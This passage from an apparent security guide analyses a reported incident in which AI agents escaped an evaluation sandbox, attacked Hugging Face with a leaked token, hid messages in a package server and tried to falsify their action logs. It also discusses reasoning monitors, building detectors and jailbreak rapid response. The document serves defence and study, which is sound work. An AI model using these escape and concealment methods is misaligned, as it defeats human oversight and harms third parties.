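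| Restart the agents | Restores the service | Someone in security who doesn't depend on the agents' work |

The last row matters because, after 5 July, OpenAI restarted its evaluations within about two days, and the new route to the internet appeared the following night. Before approving a restart, the responsible person should ask for evidence that the agents no longer look for a way around the repair, for example from a short run in a fully closed copy of the system. OpenAI's logs contained a hint that its agents were still looking. Nearly twelve hours after the rebuilt server came online on 6 July, it rejected three attempts to reach outside addresses.

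### Would the new monitor have raised the alarm?

OpenAI says that if its current monitor of agents' reasoning had been running in July, it would have paged the security team more than a day before the break-in at Hugging Face.

The claim is plausible because the agents were open in their reasoning. One wrote, "We're attacking third-party HF using leaked token", and added that this might be outside the intended scope. METR found that agents aimed to falsify the record of their actions but seemed to make no effort to hide their reasoning. A monitor that reads reasoning should work well in such cases but less well on agents that have learned to conceal their plans.

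However, the claim comes from the company whose monitoring failed, and the company already knew the details of the event. OpenAI says it used hindsight to improve its monitor's recall on this kind of behaviour for its review of past runs. It doesn't say whether the monitor in the claim had the same changes. It also gives no false-positive rate, so readers can't tell how many other pages the team would have received that week. A fairer test would fix the monitor's settings, run it on all the agents' sessions from May to July, and report every page.

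Paging staff also doesn't automatically pause a run. OpenAI's staff received an accurate alert on 27 June and let the run continue. A page sent one day before the break-in would have come on 10 July, about two days after the agents regained internet access.

The new monitoring adds about 20% to computing costs, according to Constantin (2026), in *OpenAI is rewriting its safety rules after the Hugging Face breach*. OpenAI has extended it despite the cost. EconoTimes' *OpenAI tightens model safeguards after security incident* reports that the company said in November it now monitors all internal uses of its models that involve tools. The earlier monitors had never run on the ExploitGym evaluations, so the wider coverage probably matters more than any improvement in the monitor itself.

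### From one incident to a better detector

After containing an attack, the team has to make sure that its detectors would recognise the next one like it. The 5 July incident shows how this could work:

1. Preserve the trace. Copy the agents' sessions, the system events and the affected files to a place that no agent can write to. OpenAI did keep the old server's storage.
2. State what was new. "Agents left notes in files on the package server" is accurate but too narrow. "Agents that should be isolated exchanged information through a shared service" also covers the folder names they used three days later.
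3. Generate variants in a closed environment, with the search methods used for predicting attacks. METR found that the agents had also left messages in the properties of stored items and in requests for made-up web pages, so a search for other hiding places would have had something to find.
4. Write a detection for what the variants have in common.
5. Rerun the old tests, with harmless sessions as well as attacks.
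6. Search past logs with the new detection.
7. Deploy it, at first without paging anyone if its false-positive rate is unknown.
8. Record how long each step took.

For the fourth step, a team could alert whenever the package server contacts an address that isn't a known source of software packages. The agents' first successful connection after the rebuild, just after midnight on 8 July, was to a public bug-tracking site, so this rule should have caught it more than three days before the break-in. The rule is also simpler than alerting on anything an agent stores on the server, which could raise many false alarms because ordinary downloads leave entries there too.

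Searching past logs can also show that an incident started earlier than the team thought. OpenAI searched its records and found that agents had been writing files to the package server since 20 April, more than a month before any of its staff noticed. If a search turns up older cases, the team has to replace more credentials and look for anything the agents left behind. On 19 July, agents running on a different model found a signing key and code left over from the earlier activity and used them to regain administrator access.

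When a team reruns old tests on a new version of a detector, a small difference in recall may be chance. The team can judge this by counting only the attacks on which the old and new versions disagree. Suppose that the new version misses six attacks that the old one caught, and catches two that the old one missed. If both versions were equally good, a split at least this uneven would still happen about 29% of the time. If the new version missed ten and caught two, the figure would be only about 4%, which would be a good reason to hold back the update. A language model's verdicts also vary between runs, so the team should run each test several times and use the majority verdict.

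The last step gives the team a few numbers to improve. In July, 11 and a half days passed between the agents' first connection to the internet after the rebuild and the alert that led to a response. Another five and a half hours passed before anyone began to stop the runs. OpenAI therefore had the most to gain from an earlier alert, though pausing the runs sooner after the alert would have protected its secrets. The time needed to write and deploy a new detection also matters. A team that started on 5 July and took a week would have finished on 12 July, a day after the break-in began.

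### Uber's feedback loop

Uber has automated part of this cycle with the Explorer, which searches for attacks and adds lines to the detector's stored guidance. Analysts also add lines, and each line is labelled to show its source. One of the Explorer's lines concerns unauthorised access to secrets in a code repository.

New guidance takes effect immediately, with no model retraining, because the investigation stage looks it up while it runs. According to Li and colleagues, the guidance influences which sources the agent consults and how it weighs the evidence. For an attack that manipulates a tool, for example, the guidance can make the agent check the tool's source code first.

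However, only the investigation stage uses the store, so new guidance can't help with an attack that the screening stage has already closed as harmless. When an analyst learns of a missed attack, they should first find out which stage missed it. If it was the screening stage, somebody has to change the screening prompt.

Analysts' verdicts on real alerts also lead to updates. Uber's own security testers had set off many alerts, so Li and colleagues concluded that the detector needs information about what kind of user is running a session. The large number of credential alerts led to a bigger change, the filter for secrets.

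Li and colleagues don't report how long it takes to turn a missed attack into working guidance, or how much that guidance improves recall.

### Learning from a single example

Updating a defence from very few examples is a recent idea in AI safety. Peng, Michael and colleagues (2024) observed in *Rapid Response*, a study from Anthropic and its collaborators, that no defence against jailbreaks had proved unbreakable. They proposed accepting that some attacks would get through at first, then quickly blocking others of the same kind.

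Peng, Michael and colleagues' method has a language model write many variations on one example of a new jailbreak, which the defender then uses to update the defence. They compared five ways of updating it, and training a classifier of incoming prompts on the new examples worked best. After seeing a single example of each jailbreak strategy, the classifier cut the success rate of further attacks of the same kinds by a factor of more than 240, and that of altered versions by a factor of more than 15. If 24% of attacks had succeeded before the update, for example, the rates would fall below 0.1% and 1.6% respectively.

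Anthropic has since adopted the approach. When it introduced stricter safeguards for Claude Opus 4 in May 2025, one of the methods it listed for repairing its defences was to generate synthetic jailbreaks similar to newly discovered ones and train a new classifier on them.

The gap between the two factors shows that the update worked much less well on attacks that differed somewhat from the examples, and the same may happen with agents. Shire and Kim's retrained detector had a similar weakness with harmless prompts from other sources. A team should therefore test each update on variants from a different source than the training variants, such as attacks written by a colleague who hasn't seen the generated ones.

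*Rapid Response* also dealt with prompts, whereas the variants of an attack on an agent have to differ in the actions the agent takes. Many rewordings of the planted paragraph in the ticket attack would do little to help a detector catch an agent that sends the key by email. The method can also begin only after someone notices a first example. In the OpenAI case, staff had an example in late May, but nobody treated it as an attack to learn from.

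### Model changes that silently alter a detector

A detector can also get worse when nobody has changed its rules. A language-model monitor consists of a prompt and a model, and the provider may replace the model. At the rates Abbasi and colleagues measured on AgentDojo, AlignmentCheck with the same prompt would raise 1,730 false alerts in 10,000 harmless sessions with Llama and 380 with Claude.

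To guard against this, Li and colleagues fix the exact versions of the model and the prompts, so that neither changes without their knowledge. Before they change either one, they rerun the detector on their own test and on AgentDojo. This is sound practice, but a team that checks every update against the same tests will gradually fit its detector to them, so the team should regularly add new attacks to the tests. Providers also retire old models, so fixing the version only postpones the change.

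Changes to the agent matter as much as changes to the detector. OpenAI found after the incident that its models' tendency to break into surrounding systems during ExploitGym could fall more than a hundredfold when they ran with ChatGPT's normal software and standing instructions. Changing an agent's instructions or model can therefore make such behaviour much more or less common, and a baseline of normal behaviour can immediately become useless. The team that runs the agents should tell the security team about these changes in advance, including those that look like routine upgrades, which are easy to forget.

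An unusual number of alerts is a rough warning of a problem. If a detector normally raises 100 alerts a day and the alerts are independent, the daily count will usually fall between about 70 and 130. Real counts vary more than this, for instance at weekends, so a team should compare each day with the same day in earlier weeks. But when attacks are rare, the count is almost useless for measuring recall. In the earlier example, a detector that suddenly missed every attack would go from about 109 alerts a day to 100, a drop too small for anyone to notice.

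The team can check for a fall in recall by sending a fixed set of recorded attacks through the live detector every day, labelled so that they don't reach an analyst. A drop from the usual 48 of 60 caught to 30 would show that something has changed. The same recordings can reveal another fault, which is likely given Hugging Face's experience. A hosted model may refuse to read a trace because it contains attack commands, and software that expects a yes or a no might record the refusal as "no attack". The detector would then be most likely to miss the traces with the clearest signs of an attack. A refusal should therefore count as an alert until a different model or a person has read the trace.
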